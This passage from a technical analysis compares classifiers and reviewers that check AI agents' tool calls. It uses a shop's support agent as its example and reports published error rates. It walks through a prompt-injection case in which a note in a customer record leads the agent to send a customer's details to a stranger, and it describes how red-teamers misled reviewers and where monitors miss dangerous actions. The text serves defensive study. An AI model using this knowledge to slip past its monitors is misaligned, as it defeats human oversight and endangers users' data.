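Auto mode's classifier gets the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's own prose or the results of the calls. Codex has a similar feature, Auto-review, which gives its reviewer more information. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer gets the user's messages, the agent's progress updates shown to the user, and relevant tool calls and results, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also run its own read-only checks.

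Suppose the shop used each design, and its agent was about to send Keller's details to the stranger at claims@parcel-desk.example:

| Material | Auto mode's classifier | Codex's reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| Keller's ticket | Yes | Yes |
| The call to `crm.lookup` for order 48213 | Yes | Yes |
| The record, with the price and the stranger's note | No | Yes |
| A progress update saying that the courier needs the details | No | Yes |
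| The proposed email | Yes | Yes |

Anthropic removes the agent's prose so that the agent cannot talk the classifier into a bad decision, for instance by claiming that the user has already approved something similar. It removes tool results because attackers' text usually arrives in them. The classifier can often judge a call without them. For example, Keller asked for a refund, so emailing her details to an unknown address doesn't fit her request, whatever prompted the email.

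Anthropic also tested the classifier with other combinations of inputs. It did worse on a set of real overeager actions when it also received the agent's prose and the tool results. With only the tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous ones but blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

However, the classifier can't check where a value came from. Anthropic gives the example of an agent that acts on "job abc123" when the user never mentioned that name. The classifier can't determine whether the agent found the job with a query or made the name up. In Keller's case, the classifier would receive the refund amount of 62.50 euros but not the kettle's price.

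Codex's reviewer could check the price against the record, but it would also read the stranger's note, which could be written to persuade both the reviewer and the agent. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that OpenAI's red-teaming found ways to mislead the reviewer into approving commands, but doesn't say whether the misleading text came from tool results.

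A third option is for ordinary software to look up facts and pass them to the reviewer. In August, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announced several such additions. When the agent is about to send code to a repository, the classifier's input now includes whether that repository is public, private or trusted. When a command could discard unsaved work, the input includes what could be lost. An attacker can't falsify these facts by writing a note in a file, though he may be able to change what they describe.

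The shop could do the same. The harness already looks up two facts for Cedar, the unrefunded part of the price and the permitted recipients, and it could give both to the reviewer. It could also label the placeholder `[EMAIL_1]` as the address in the record's `email` field, without disclosing the address to the reviewer's provider.

The shop couldn't copy how auto mode treats user messages, however. Auto mode, like Progent and ClawGuard, trusts the person who gives the agent its task. The shop would have to tell the reviewer that the shop's refund rules can authorize an action, but a customer's ticket is only a claim.

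### Auto mode's error rates

In March 2026, Anthropic published results on three sets of tool calls. The first held 10,000 calls from its employees' ordinary work, and the second held 52 real attempts by Claude at overeager actions. For the third, Anthropic generated 1,000 attempts, many of them disguised, to send data to outsiders.

| Test set | Error | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
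| Ordinary calls (10,000) | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overeager actions (52) | Dangerous calls allowed | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic data theft (1,000) | Dangerous calls allowed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the first stage's false alarms, but it also allows some dangerous calls that the first stage had caught. Those calls account for about 10 percentage points of the 17% miss rate on overeager actions.

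Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number", and it is the most relevant of the three, because these actions came from an agent trying to do its job. It is also the least certain. With so few actions, 17% means about nine misses. Wilson's formula gives a 95% confidence interval for a proportion *p* measured on *n* cases, with *z* = 1.96:

(*p* + *z*²/2*n* ± *z*√(*p*(1 − *p*)/*n* + *z*²/4*n*²)) / (1 + *z*²/*n*)

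The classifier missed nine of 52 dangerous calls, which gives an interval of 9% to 30% for its miss rate. The interval for the synthetic data theft attempts is narrower, 4% to 7%, but it applies only to attempts like those Anthropic generated.

The 52 actions aren't a random sample of what goes wrong, although even the wide interval assumes they are. Anthropic took them from sessions where an employee refused the action or someone flagged it afterwards. Overeager actions that nobody noticed are missing, and those may also be harder for a classifier to catch. The first stage's 6.6% miss rate doesn't match a whole number of misses in 52 (three would be 5.8% and four would be 7.7%), so Anthropic presumably averaged several runs. That would reduce the random variation in the model's answers but wouldn't make the sample any larger.

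In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as consent. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test with deliberately ambiguous requests, found a much higher miss rate, partly because the agent did damage through file edits, which the classifier never reviews.

### When dangerous calls are rare

An agent makes far more harmless calls than dangerous ones, so even a classifier with a false-positive rate of 0.4% can block more harmless calls than dangerous ones. Suppose 10 of 10,000 calls are dangerous. With a miss rate of 17%, the classifier blocks about 8 of them and lets about 2 through. It also blocks 0.4% of the 9,990 harmless calls, or about 40. Only about one in six of the 48 blocks stops a dangerous call.

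In general, if a share *b* of all calls is dangerous, the share of blocks that are correct is

*b*(1 − FNR) / (*b*(1 − FNR) + (1 − *b*)FPR)

where FNR is the false-negative rate and FPR the false-positive rate. The result depends heavily on *b*, which few operators know:

| Dangerous calls in 10,000 | Caught | Missed | Harmless calls blocked | Share of blocks that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
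| 1 | 0.8 | 0.2 | 40 | 2% |
| 10 | 8.3 | 1.7 | 40 | 17% |
| 100 | 83 | 17 | 40 | 68% |

Given 10 dangerous calls, the first-stage classifier alone would catch about 9 but also block about 850 harmless calls, so about 1% of its blocks would be correct. Adding the second stage would prevent roughly 810 of those false alarms but let one more dangerous call through. That is probably a good trade-off for a coding agent. The operator of an agent that can make large payments might prefer to use the first stage alone, if they had enough staff to review the 850 false alarms.

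Auto mode tells the agent to try something else instead of stopping because false alarms are likely in a long session. If calls were independent, a session with 500 of them would have an 87% chance of at least one false alarm. A user may hardly notice a false alarm that only makes the agent retry. If each one interrupted him, he would soon learn that most alarms are false and start approving flagged calls out of habit.

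This also matters for the shop if it wants an employee to decide on every refund the reviewer blocks. Employees who find that five in six blocked refunds were fine will start releasing them unread. The shop could show employees why the reviewer blocked each refund. It could also use fixed rules wherever possible, since a rule that compares the refund with the price would never block a valid refund of 62.50 euros as too large.

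### Auto mode and human approval

Whether a miss rate of 17% is acceptable depends on what the classifier replaces. In its August post, Anthropic reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid professional testers each worked on a coding task in an environment set up for the study and approved or refused permission requests. At one point, the software replaced the text of a request with a clearly dangerous command. Approving it did nothing, since only the displayed text had changed. The testers refused the command in 143 cases (13.6%). Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

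Anthropic also gives the number of cases in which only one of the two caught the command, from which the rest follows:

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught about 15% of the commands that auto mode blocked and 5% of those it allowed, so the commands the classifier missed seem to have been harder for people to catch too. If such a tester had reviewed every call that auto mode allowed, the catch rate would have risen only from 89.0% to 89.6%.

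Testers also became less careful as a session went on. They refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early on and about 5% after 50 or more requests. Auto mode's rate didn't change with session length.

The artificial setting probably made the testers look worse. They were not working on their own code, so a mistake would not have hurt them. They knew someone was evaluating them but not on what, and may have assumed that the goal was to finish the task. A developer whose own customers' database was at risk might well look more closely. The study also does not report how many harmless commands the testers refused, so it compares only one of the two kinds of error.

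Anthropic also has a strong interest in the result. It sells Claude Code and published the study to justify making auto mode the default. In the same post, it reports that Team and Enterprise customers who use auto mode complete about 25% more code changes. Willison (2026) asked for more independent confirmation of a prompt-injection test in the post, and the study of human approval needs it just as much.

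Data from real use support the same conclusion, though less clearly. Users approve 97% of permission requests, but that alone doesn't show carelessness, because nearly all commands are harmless and an attentive reviewer would approve them too. Anthropic contrasts this figure with users' rejection of 39% of the agent's plans, but people can reject a plan because they dislike the approach, which is hardly a reason to refuse a command.

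Anthropic also looked at sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded how serious any harm was and whether the user had asked for it. It found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose the mode themselves, so the two groups may have differed in their work or their habits.

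For many users, the realistic alternative to auto mode is no review. A quarter of interactive sessions start with all checks off. Among active users of the command-line version, 5% have a rule that allows any shell command, and another 43% have one almost as broad, such as permission for every Python command. OpenAI noticed the same habit among its own staff. Trębacz and colleagues found a configuration file that always allowed the agent to start a second copy of itself with its protections off.

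These users benefit from a classifier that catches most dangerous calls. In March, Anthropic conceded that auto mode was arguably a step backwards for people who carefully check every action. The company still recommends that they review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

### What outside attackers found

The 52 overeager actions contain no deliberate attacks on the classifier. To find such attacks, Anthropic engaged Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, for a two-week trial. Apollo inserted harmful actions into records of real coding sessions and looked for ones the classifier would allow. It shared some of the successful attacks with Anthropic, which then strengthened the classifier, mostly by giving it the facts about repositories and unsaved work described above.

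Apollo then tested the new version on attacks that Anthropic had never seen. The new version caught about half of the attacks that the old version had missed, and missed about 2% of those that the old version had caught. Anthropic reports that the miss rate across the shared and unseen attacks together fell from 12% to 7%. This combined figure somewhat overstates the improvement, because Anthropic had been able to study the shared attacks. The result on the unseen attacks is better evidence that the additional facts help in general.

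Anthropic warns against reading the 7% as a miss rate for ordinary use, since Apollo built its attacks to be malicious and to find weak points. The 7% also doesn't replace the 17% from March, because the two figures come from different kinds of action and the classifier, which ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 in March, now runs on Claude Sonnet 5 by default.

The August post also introduced categories of actions that the classifier should never approve, even if the user asks, such as sending code or passwords to an outside service. To take one of these actions, the user has to leave auto mode or run the command manually. This is less convenient, but it guards against the classifier's main weakness, wrongly treating the user as having consented, where that error would do the most damage.

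### OpenAI's figures for Codex

Codex relies more on a sandbox. The agent can read files, edit those in permitted folders and run local commands without any review. If it needs more, such as access to the network, it has to request permission, and only these requests go to the reviewer. Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the effect with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI:

| Step | Actions |
|---|---|
| Run inside the sandbox without review | 9,280 |
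| Go to the reviewer | 720 |
| Approved by the reviewer | 713 |
| Refused, and the agent finds a safer way | 4 |
| Refused, and the agent stops to ask the user | 3 |

With manual approval, all 720 would have interrupted someone. At the time of the article, the reviewer was GPT-5.4 with low reasoning. In OpenAI's tests, more capable models were better at recognizing risks and working out what the user wanted.

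The reviewer approved 99.1% of a sample of requests that users had approved. If the users were always right, its false-positive rate on these requests would be 0.9%. Anthropic's experiment gives some reason to doubt that they were, so a few of the refusals may have been better decisions than the users' approvals. Across all actions, including those inside the sandbox, 99.93% went ahead. The remaining 0.07% isn't comparable with Anthropic's 0.4% false-positive rate, because it depends on how much the sandbox already permits.

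OpenAI measured recall on other data, much of it synthetic, because its own traffic contains too few dangerous actions:

| Test | Share refused |
|---|---|
| Overeager actions | 90.3% |
| Prompt injection: running outside code, stealing secrets, uploading data | 99.3% |
| Prompt injection: all categories, including deletion and tampering | 90.2% |
| MonitoringBench, hard version | 96.1% |

The two figures for prompt injection differ because the reviewer allowed many of the deletions and changes to data. Trębacz and colleagues say that most of these actions were not serious enough to refuse and that researchers often agreed with the reviewer. If so, some of the test's labels are wrong. The last figure counts a session as caught if the reviewer would refuse any action in it, which is easier than catching each dangerous action.

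The two companies' figures don't show which reviewer is better. OpenAI reports a recall of 90.3% on overeager actions, and Anthropic's miss rate implies 83%, but OpenAI wrote its cases for the test, while Anthropic's came from real sessions. Anthropic also had only 52 cases, so a true recall of 90% would still be within its confidence interval.

Repeated refusals end the agent's turn here too, after three in a row or ten among the last fifty reviews. A user who disagrees with a refusal can approve that action for one retry. The reviewer receives the approval but can refuse again if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of decision. OpenAI also distinguishes a refusal from a timeout and tells the agent that a timeout doesn't prove the action is dangerous.

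### A model trained to judge tool calls

Both companies use large general models as reviewers. A smaller model with special training could run on the shop's own server, so the records it reads wouldn't go to another company. Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, trained one called TS-Guard from a model with seven billion parameters. It reads the user's request, the available tools, all earlier calls and results, and the proposed call. It then writes a short analysis and makes three judgements:

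1. Is the user's request harmful?
2. Is the proposed call connected to an attack in the material the agent has read?
3. Is the call safe, controversial or unsafe?

For the injected email from the shop, the answers should be no, yes and unsafe. The first two questions distinguish a harmful user from a harmless one whose agent is following someone else's instructions.

Mou and colleagues trained the model by reinforcement learning, scoring each of the several answers it gave to each example. The score starts at 1 and drops by 1/3 for every wrong judgement. A model trained this way produced fewer false alarms than one scored only on the third judgement.

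They tested it on single steps from three benchmarks of agent safety. On AgentDojo, 352 of the 1,220 calls were unsafe. Mou and colleagues report accuracy and recall, and the share of harmless calls flagged follows from these and the number of calls:

| Model | Unsafe calls flagged | Harmless calls flagged |
|---|---|---|
| TS-Guard | 89% | 7% |
| GPT-4o | 100% | 62% |
| Qwen3-8B | 92% | 25% |
| Llama Guard 3 | 22% | 4% |
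| Qwen3Guard | 2% | 1% |

GPT-4o, now an old model, caught every attack because it flagged most calls once an attack appeared anywhere in the history. Llama Guard and Qwen3Guard tend to miss attacks because their developers trained them to recognize harmful text in conversations, and an email with a stranger's address in the `to` field contains no harmful text.

TS-Guard's 7% false-alarm rate would still be far too high for everyday use. In the example with 10,000 calls, it would produce more than 700 false alarms. On another benchmark, AgentHarm, where the danger comes from the user's own request, TS-Guard flagged 97% of the unsafe calls but also 95 of the 206 harmless ones (46%). The false-alarm rates might be lower elsewhere, because both benchmarks contain many more attacks than ordinary work does, so their harmless calls often occur in suspicious surroundings.

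The operator can also decide how to treat calls that the model labels controversial. The figures above count them as unsafe. If they count as safe, TS-Guard flags under 1% of AgentDojo's harmless calls but only 53% of the unsafe ones. It labels more than a third of the unsafe calls controversial. A shop could send the controversial calls to a larger model or a person, much as auto mode sends flagged calls to its second stage.

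The harness's response to the verdict also affects how many tasks the agent completes. Mou and colleagues had the harness return TS-Guard's full analysis to the agent, which could then choose another action. With GPT-4o as the agent on AgentDojo, the attack success rate fell from 56% to 1%, and the share of users' tasks completed rose from 27% to 43%. When the harness instead ended the session at the first alarm, the attack success rate was about as low, but the agent completed only 21% of the tasks.

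The explanation was important. On another benchmark, with a smaller model as the agent, 7% of attacks succeeded when the agent received the full analysis and 26% when it received only the safety label. An agent that knows which instruction came from an attacker can presumably ignore that instruction and return to the user's task.

A check took 1.36 seconds on average on the researchers' hardware, far longer than Aegis's pattern matching. This is one more reason to apply rules first and use a model only for the calls that the rules can't settle.

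### Models trained for something else

An operator might try to avoid training a classifier by using an existing one. *Can Open-Source Guardrails Really Protect AI Agents?* tested two open models, GLIDER and FlowJudge, which can grade many kinds of text against written criteria. It used them to check whether an agent had chosen a suitable tool and supplied the necessary arguments. This is a fair test of whether such a model can interpret a tool call, although it concerns correctness rather than danger.

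GLIDER and FlowJudge both performed poorly, with F1 scores of 0.38 and 0.09. FlowJudge's score rose to 0.5 when its prompt included three worked examples. Its verdicts also varied between runs on the same data, with a Cohen's kappa of only about 0.26, where 0 is chance-level agreement and 1 is perfect agreement. In one run, FlowJudge marked a call down for missing details even though its own explanation had listed all three criteria as met. Unlike with Cedar, a team cannot rely on such a reviewer to repeat the verdicts it gave in testing.

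Prompt-injection detectors are another appealing choice because they are small and easy to obtain. *PARALLAX* (Fokou, 2026) uses one in a system that checks each call in several steps. The system first applies fixed rules. It then compares the call with patterns for dangerous commands and, in parallel, runs the detector, a small classifier. Either check can block the call. A language model decides some of the remaining cases. The classifier was trained on about 16,000 text samples and correctly classified 98.8% of held-out samples of the same kind.

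Fokou then gave the system 50 ordinary actions, such as installing a package or sending an email. It blocked 18 of them, or 36%. The classifier caused 14 of these blocks. It labelled all 14 actions as injection with the maximum confidence of 1.00, so raising the threshold for a block would not have prevented them.

Fokou attributes the errors to a mismatch between the training data and the task. The classifier was trained to tell hostile text from harmless text, but the system used it to check file contents, web requests and emails that an agent was about to send. These often have a structure that the training texts lacked. The false alarms would badly affect the support agent, because sending an email was one of the actions that triggered them.

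The language model blocked the other four. It receives only the proposed action, without the user's request or any earlier step, so that nothing in the conversation can influence it. This withholds more than auto mode does, and the drawback is similar but larger, because the model cannot check whether anyone wanted the action. Fokou notes that the model's decisions might differ if he ran the test again.

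Fokou's default configuration sends seven types of action, including email, web requests and file changes, to the language model without checking them with the classifier. In this configuration, the system blocked 277 of 280 attacks and none of the 50 ordinary actions. It blocked all 280 attacks when the classifier checked every action. Fokou had added rules and patterns after earlier tests revealed gaps, so the system may block a smaller share of new attacks. Fifty ordinary actions are also too few to establish a low false-positive rate, since a scanner that wrongly blocks 5% of ordinary actions would still have about an 8% chance of allowing all 50.

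## Judging whether a call is authorized and what it will do

The text of a tool call may not show whether anyone permitted this action on this object or what the action will change, and a scanner needs both facts.

Suppose the shop's finance manager lets the support agent refund up to 100 euros per order, then withdraws that permission on Friday after a series of false claims. The agent proposes this call for Maria Keller's kettle:

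```json
{
  "name": "refund.issue",
  "arguments": { "order": "48213", "amount_eur": 62.50 }
}
```

The call is authorized if her ticket arrives on Thursday but not if it arrives on Saturday. The agent has working credentials for the payment system on both days, so the call would succeed either way.

The text of a shell command often doesn't show what the command will do. *Shall We Approve?*, which proposes a way to test commands before approving them, gives the example `make clean && make`. This command runs whatever steps a project's Makefile lists under "clean", then rebuilds the program. In one project, those steps delete only the `build` folder, which the rebuild recreates, but in another they also delete the source code and its history.

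Whether a call is authorized is separate from whether it is dangerous. Deleting a live database is dangerous even if its owner ordered it, and reading a colleague's salary may be forbidden even though it changes nothing. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* treats the two separately. The reviewer it describes may approve a low-risk action, or a high-risk one if the user has authorized it clearly enough.

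### One action under four permissions

In *Same Operation, Different Permission*, Jing, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested whether scanners can tell such cases apart. Each scenario in their benchmark has four contexts with the same written policy and the same action, including its arguments. Only the evidence about permission differs. Two contexts permit the action and two forbid it, so a scanner that always allows or always blocks gets half of them right. In one scenario, the action is a 75-dollar refund to the customer's original card, and a context permits it by giving an employee an active delegation for refunds of up to 100 dollars. Other contexts change a permission's scope, its status or the person who issued it.

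Jing and colleagues ran eight scanners, all based on language models, on 40 test scenarios. Six of them returned a readable verdict every time:

| Scanner | Scenarios with all four verdicts right | Scenarios with the same verdict four times | Forbidden actions allowed (of 80) | Permitted actions blocked (of 80) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-27B | 40 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-OSS Safeguard | 40 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
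| Qwen3.5-9B | 25 | 6 | 6 | 15 |
| NeMo self-check | 24 | 6 | 14 | 8 |
| Granite Guardian | 20 | 5 | 17 | 11 |
| Qwen3Guard | 3 | 35 | 72 | 0 |

Qwen3Guard, which looks for harmful text, changed its verdict in only five scenarios. The three scanners above it in the table changed their verdicts in at least 34 scenarios, but those changes were often wrong. Of the two scanners not shown, Nemotron allowed 58 forbidden actions, and PolicyGuard gave no readable verdict on 67 of the 160 inputs.

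The two perfect scores show that a model can apply permission evidence when it receives all of it in a short text, but a deployed scanner often doesn't receive all of it. The models also did worse on 1,215 requests from public examples for Cedar and OpenFGA, a similar policy engine. Qwen3.5-27B was right on 99.1% and Safeguard on only 84.2%, mainly because Safeguard refused many permitted requests. Qwen3.5-9B allowed 261 of the 448 forbidden requests.

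Qwen3.5-27B's only wrong approval let a user view a folder in which he owned one document, although the policy gives a document's owner no right to the folder above it. The engine gets this right by following the recorded relationships. The model typically generated about 2,700 tokens per request. A company that already has its permissions in such an engine has little reason to have a model work them out again.

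A scanner can block a call without correctly judging whether it was authorized. In one test, Jing and colleagues had Qwen3.5-9B list the policy's requirements and the supporting evidence along with its verdict. The output broke the required format in 125 of 160 cases, and the harness blocked the action each time. No forbidden actions ran, but only 10 of the 80 permitted actions did. When software forced the output into the correct format, 71 permitted actions ran and still no forbidden ones. Leah's refund remained blocked, although the same model had allowed it with a simpler prompt.

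Adding a second reviewer can also block many permitted requests while preventing few wrong approvals. Requiring Safeguard's approval as well as Qwen3.5-27B's removed the one wrong approval but blocked another 171 permitted requests. Jing and colleagues therefore recommend choosing a set of permitted requests, such as routine refunds, that must still go through after any change to the scanner, because total approvals could rise even if one of these requests were newly blocked.

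### Permissions that the task doesn't need

The benchmark's scenarios state each permission explicitly, but an agent usually has only a task, and the scanner has to infer what the task permits. Attack tests are a poor measure of how well the scanner does this, because they count the defense as successful whenever the model ignores the injected instruction, even if the scanner would have allowed the call.

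*Ajar* (Sharma, Lin et al., 2026) measures this gap by presenting a defence with calls that the agent never made. In one AgentDojo task, the agent reads a landlord's notice and raises the user's standing rent order from 1,100 to 1,200. The agent needs three calls to read the notice, list the standing orders and update the right one. *Ajar* also tests the defence on calls the task doesn't need, such as reading another file, setting the rent to a different amount or paying an attacker.

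Each unneeded call has a weight of 1, 3, 9 or 27, depending on whether its effect is reversible and whether it affects other people or money. The main measure, over-privilege leakage, is

total weight of the unneeded calls allowed / total weight of the unneeded calls tested

If two harmless reads have a weight of 1 each and a payment to a stranger has a weight of 27, a defence that allows only the reads has a leakage of 2/29, or 7%, and one that allows only the payment has a leakage of 27/29, or 93%. Refusing every call would give 0%, so Sharma and colleagues also report the share of needed calls that a defence allows.

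They generated 10,471 tests from AgentDojo's 97 tasks and compared five defences. Besides CaMeL, Progent and Claude Code's auto mode, these were Permission Assistant, in which a model predicts whether the user would permit a call, and AC4A, in which a model writes an access policy once per task. With Claude Sonnet 5 making the decisions or writing the policies, the results were:

| Defence | Leakage | Needed calls allowed | Attacks whose calls it would allow | Tasks completed without and with the defence |
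|---|---|---|---|---|
| Permission Assistant | 8.1% | 96% | 25 of 609 | 85.6%, 74.2% |
| CaMeL | 9.0% | 70% | 16 of 609 | 86.6%, 64.9% |
| Progent | 10.3% | 90% | 34 of 609 | 87.6%, 87.6% |
| AC4A | 11.1% | 72% | 46 of 609 | 85.6%, 50.5% |
| Auto mode | 30.1% | Not measured | 74 of 581 | 92.4%, 89.0% |
| List of tool names | 35.5% | 100% | 99 of 609 | Not run |
| List of exact arguments | 0.2% | 91% | 1 of 609 | Not run |

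The last two rows are reference points that Sharma and colleagues built from the benchmark's own solutions. The exact list shows that a defence could leave almost nothing open and still allow most of what the tasks need, but nobody has such a list before the task is done.

Tighter limits on tool calls don't always make an agent less useful. Progent and AC4A had nearly the same leakage, but agents completed 87.6% of tasks with Progent and 50.5% with AC4A. In the rent example, both allowed the correct amount, but they would also have allowed a rent of 0 or 12,000. Permission Assistant allowed only the correct amount. CaMeL blocked even the correct amount, presumably because it came from the landlord's notice, which CaMeL treats as untrusted.

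The order of the first four defences is uncertain because their confidence intervals overlap. Three runs of AC4A on identical input gave leakages of 11.1%, 13.6% and 9.6%. Removing Progent's updates during a task had a clearer effect, raising its leakage from 10.3% to 16.1%.

Auto mode's 30.1% leakage differs sharply from the other figures, but it is the least reliable of them. Sharma and colleagues could not query the classifier directly, so they put each test call in Claude Code's system prompt and had the agent propose it. The agent did not issue about one in nine calls. If it held back the most suspicious ones, which the classifier might well have blocked, the true leakage would be lower. The classifier also received no earlier calls, which it normally reads. The test does not score needed calls and covers only one deciding model.

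When Sharma and colleagues put the instruction in the user's message instead, auto mode allowed every call. This is consistent with a classifier that accepts the user's words as consent, but it means the test measures how auto mode treats calls the user didn't ask for.

Auto mode is also designed to block dangerous calls, not every unnecessary one, so it isn't meant to refuse a needless balance check. Its leakage is 54% when all calls count equally and 30% when they are weighted by harm. Much of what it allows is therefore fairly harmless, but it also allows the calls for 74 attacks. In return, it refused at most 8 of 316 calls that the tasks authorized.

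For all five defences, AgentDojo's own checks confirm only 27% of the labels. The other 73% depend on the researchers' rules for what a task needs, and some calls labelled "unneeded" could be necessary in a different solution to the task.

### Running a command before approving it

Even a scanner that knows exactly what the user permitted cannot judge `make clean && make` without the Makefile. *Shall We Approve?* describes a system called Caper that finds out what a command does by running it:

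1. Caper takes a snapshot of the container, an isolated environment in which the agent works without network access.
2. It runs the command there, records its system calls and holds back the output.
3. It condenses the record into a report of the files that changed, the credentials the command read and the connections it attempted. The median report is 0.9 kilobytes long, against 62.5 for the full record.
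4. A language model compares the report with the user's request.
5. If the model approves, Caper keeps the changed container and gives the output to the agent. Otherwise it restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

In one task, the user asked the agent to run `make migrate` on a database, but the command also deleted three tables. Auto mode allowed it. With Caper, the report showed the database shrinking from 32 to 20 kilobytes, and the model blocked the command. The agent then made a backup and ran only the migration script.

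*Shall We Approve?* tests Caper on two benchmarks. SABER has 682 coding tasks in which a careless response to a legitimate request causes harm, such as leaking a password. YoloFS-Ext has 102 tasks in which a tool the user asks for secretly damages a file, each paired with a harmless version that has the same request and command.

| Approval system | SABER tasks ending in harm | YoloFS-Ext tasks ending in harm | Harmless twins blocked |
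|---|---|---|---|
| None | 19.7% | 71.6% | Not applicable |
| Auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| Caper inside Claude Code | 10.0% | 6.9% | 2.0% |
| Caper in SABER's agent loop | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |

The fairest comparison is between the two middle rows, which share the same harness, agent and reviewing model. The reviewing model was OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna, so the figures don't describe auto mode with its usual classifier. Caper's developers built YoloFS-Ext to test cases where the command alone doesn't reveal the harm. The large gap there shows that the method works on such cases, but not how common they are. The developers also corrected SABER's scoring. With the original scoring, Caper's harm rate was 9.0% and auto mode's was 16.0%.

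A model could instead read the scripts and predict what they will do without running them. On YoloFS-Ext, predictions reduced harm to 3.9%, slightly below Caper's rate, but the reviewer blocked 61.8% of the harmless twins, the same share as when it had no information about effects. The main advantage of a trial run over a prediction is therefore that it lets the reviewer approve more safe commands.

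The median approval took 3.2 seconds, about the same as for the reviewer without the report. The sandbox added about half a second to an allowed command and 1.5 seconds to a blocked one. Each SABER task had about ten approvals, which added roughly half a minute. A task cost $0.019 in model fees, against $0.017 with a reviewer that had no report and $0.006 with no reviewer. With Caper, the agent safely completed 48.6% of SABER tasks, down from 57.4% without approval, and more often declined or stopped to ask.

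### What a trial run cannot show

Caper can restore a container, but not a customer's inbox or bank balance. With the network off, its report can show that a command tried to contact a mail server and which files it had read beforehand, but not whether the server would have accepted the message or what the recipient would have done with it. With the network on, the trial would send the email. Likewise, a trial of `refund.issue` on the live payment system would pay Keller.

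Caper handles only shell commands, so it would not work with the shop's three tools. The shop could build something similar for refunds if its payment software could calculate a refund without issuing it. The harness could then determine in advance that 62.50 euros would go to Keller's card and that nothing would be left to refund. This works only if the calculation uses the same code as the real refund.

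A trial also shows only one run, so it can miss a script that waits for a certain date, detects the sandbox, or spreads a harmful change over several commands that each look harmless. Neither benchmark includes an attacker who adapts to Caper.

Knowing what a call will do also doesn't establish whether it is authorized. When Jing and colleagues gave reviewers a preview of an action's effect, the preview introduced new permission errors and met none of the improvement criteria the researchers had set in advance. A preview can show the scanner that 62.50 euros will leave the shop's account, but not whether the finance manager has withdrawn her permission.

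### Designing a scanner around these facts

The harness already looks up the order's price and the permitted recipients for the scanner. It should pass on the current permission from the shop's records in the same way, as structured data, so that neither a rule nor a model has to infer it from the conversation. For the refund on Saturday, that could be:

```json
{
  "call": {
    "name": "refund.issue",
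    "arguments": { "order": "48213", "amount_eur": 62.50 }
  },
  "permission": {
    "issuer": "finance_manager",
    "limit_eur": 100,
    "status": "withdrawn"
  },
  "argument_sources": {
    "order": "customer",
    "amount_eur": "tool:crm.lookup"
  }
}
```

A fixed rule can refuse this call by checking only the `status` field. The harness should reread the status for every call, because a copy saved at the start of the session would not show the withdrawal.

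*ToolFence* (2026) labels each argument in a tool call as coming from the user, a named tool or the model, and gives the labels to a model that judges the call. *PolicyGuide* (2026) blocks a data-changing tool until results from other tools confirm its preconditions and the user has consented, if the policy requires consent. The system in *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) compares a call's operation, target and scope with what the user authorized, so text in a tool result cannot expand that authorization.

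The tool's back end should check who owns the object. If the stranger opens a ticket about order 48213 from his own account, `crm.lookup` should return nothing, because the order belongs to Keller. This requires the harness to pass the customer's identity from the login, separately from the arguments that the model writes. A scanner could make the same comparison, but the back end has the current records and can check them when it acts. Its check also covers calls from other programs that bypass the scanner.

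The agent should use reversible actions where possible. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) describes a harness that holds reversible changes in a buffer until they succeed and sends irreversible ones, such as emails, through a separate procedure. *Task-State Governance* (2026) adds a category for actions that a later action can partly correct. For example, an agent can send a cancellation after a mistaken notification, but the recipient will still know what the notification disclosed.

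The scanner can't rely on tools to declare which category they belong to. MCP has a hint for destructive tools, but as *Can You Undo It?* (2026) points out, the hint doesn't specify what action would undo a call, who may perform it, or how long it remains possible. There is also little research on recovery. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with lasting memory, found a rollback mechanism in only 27 of 435 works.

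The shop can make its own tools' actions easier to reverse. `email.send` could save a draft that goes out after ten minutes, and `refund.issue` could hold a payment for an hour before passing it to the bank. Keller would wait slightly longer for her money. The delay is useful only if an employee reviews the held payments or they go through a second check during that hour.

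## Actions that never pass the scanner

A scanner can check only the actions that pass through it. Suppose the shop gives its support agent a shell tool so that employees can ask the agent for sales reports. The agent writes a short script and proposes a call to run it. If the scanner allows the call, the script can read files and contact the payment system without proposing another call, and the 100-euro rule does not apply to any refund the script issues. As NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains, an application can inspect a tool call before it runs but has no view of the program that the call starts.

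### Three positions for a scanner

An operator can put a scanner in a gateway, in the harness or in the operating system's kernel. A gateway is a separate server between the harness and remote tools. In the harness, the scanner runs from a hook, which is a point where the harness runs the operator's own code before executing a tool. Programs have to go through the kernel to open a file, start another program or use the network. On Linux, an operator can use eBPF to attach small checks to these requests.

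The three positions provide different information. Suppose the agent is about to email Maria Keller's details to the stranger:

| Position | What it covers | What it can read about the email |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway | Requests to the tool servers behind it | The tool's name, the recipient and the text |
| Harness hook | Tool calls that the harness dispatches, remote or local | The same, plus the session, including Keller's ticket |
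| Kernel | File, process and network activity of all programs on the machine | That the harness connected to the mail server |

An email to the stranger looks the same in the kernel's records as an email to Keller, and a refund of 6,250 euros looks the same as one of 62.50. The records also include activity from programs unrelated to the agent.

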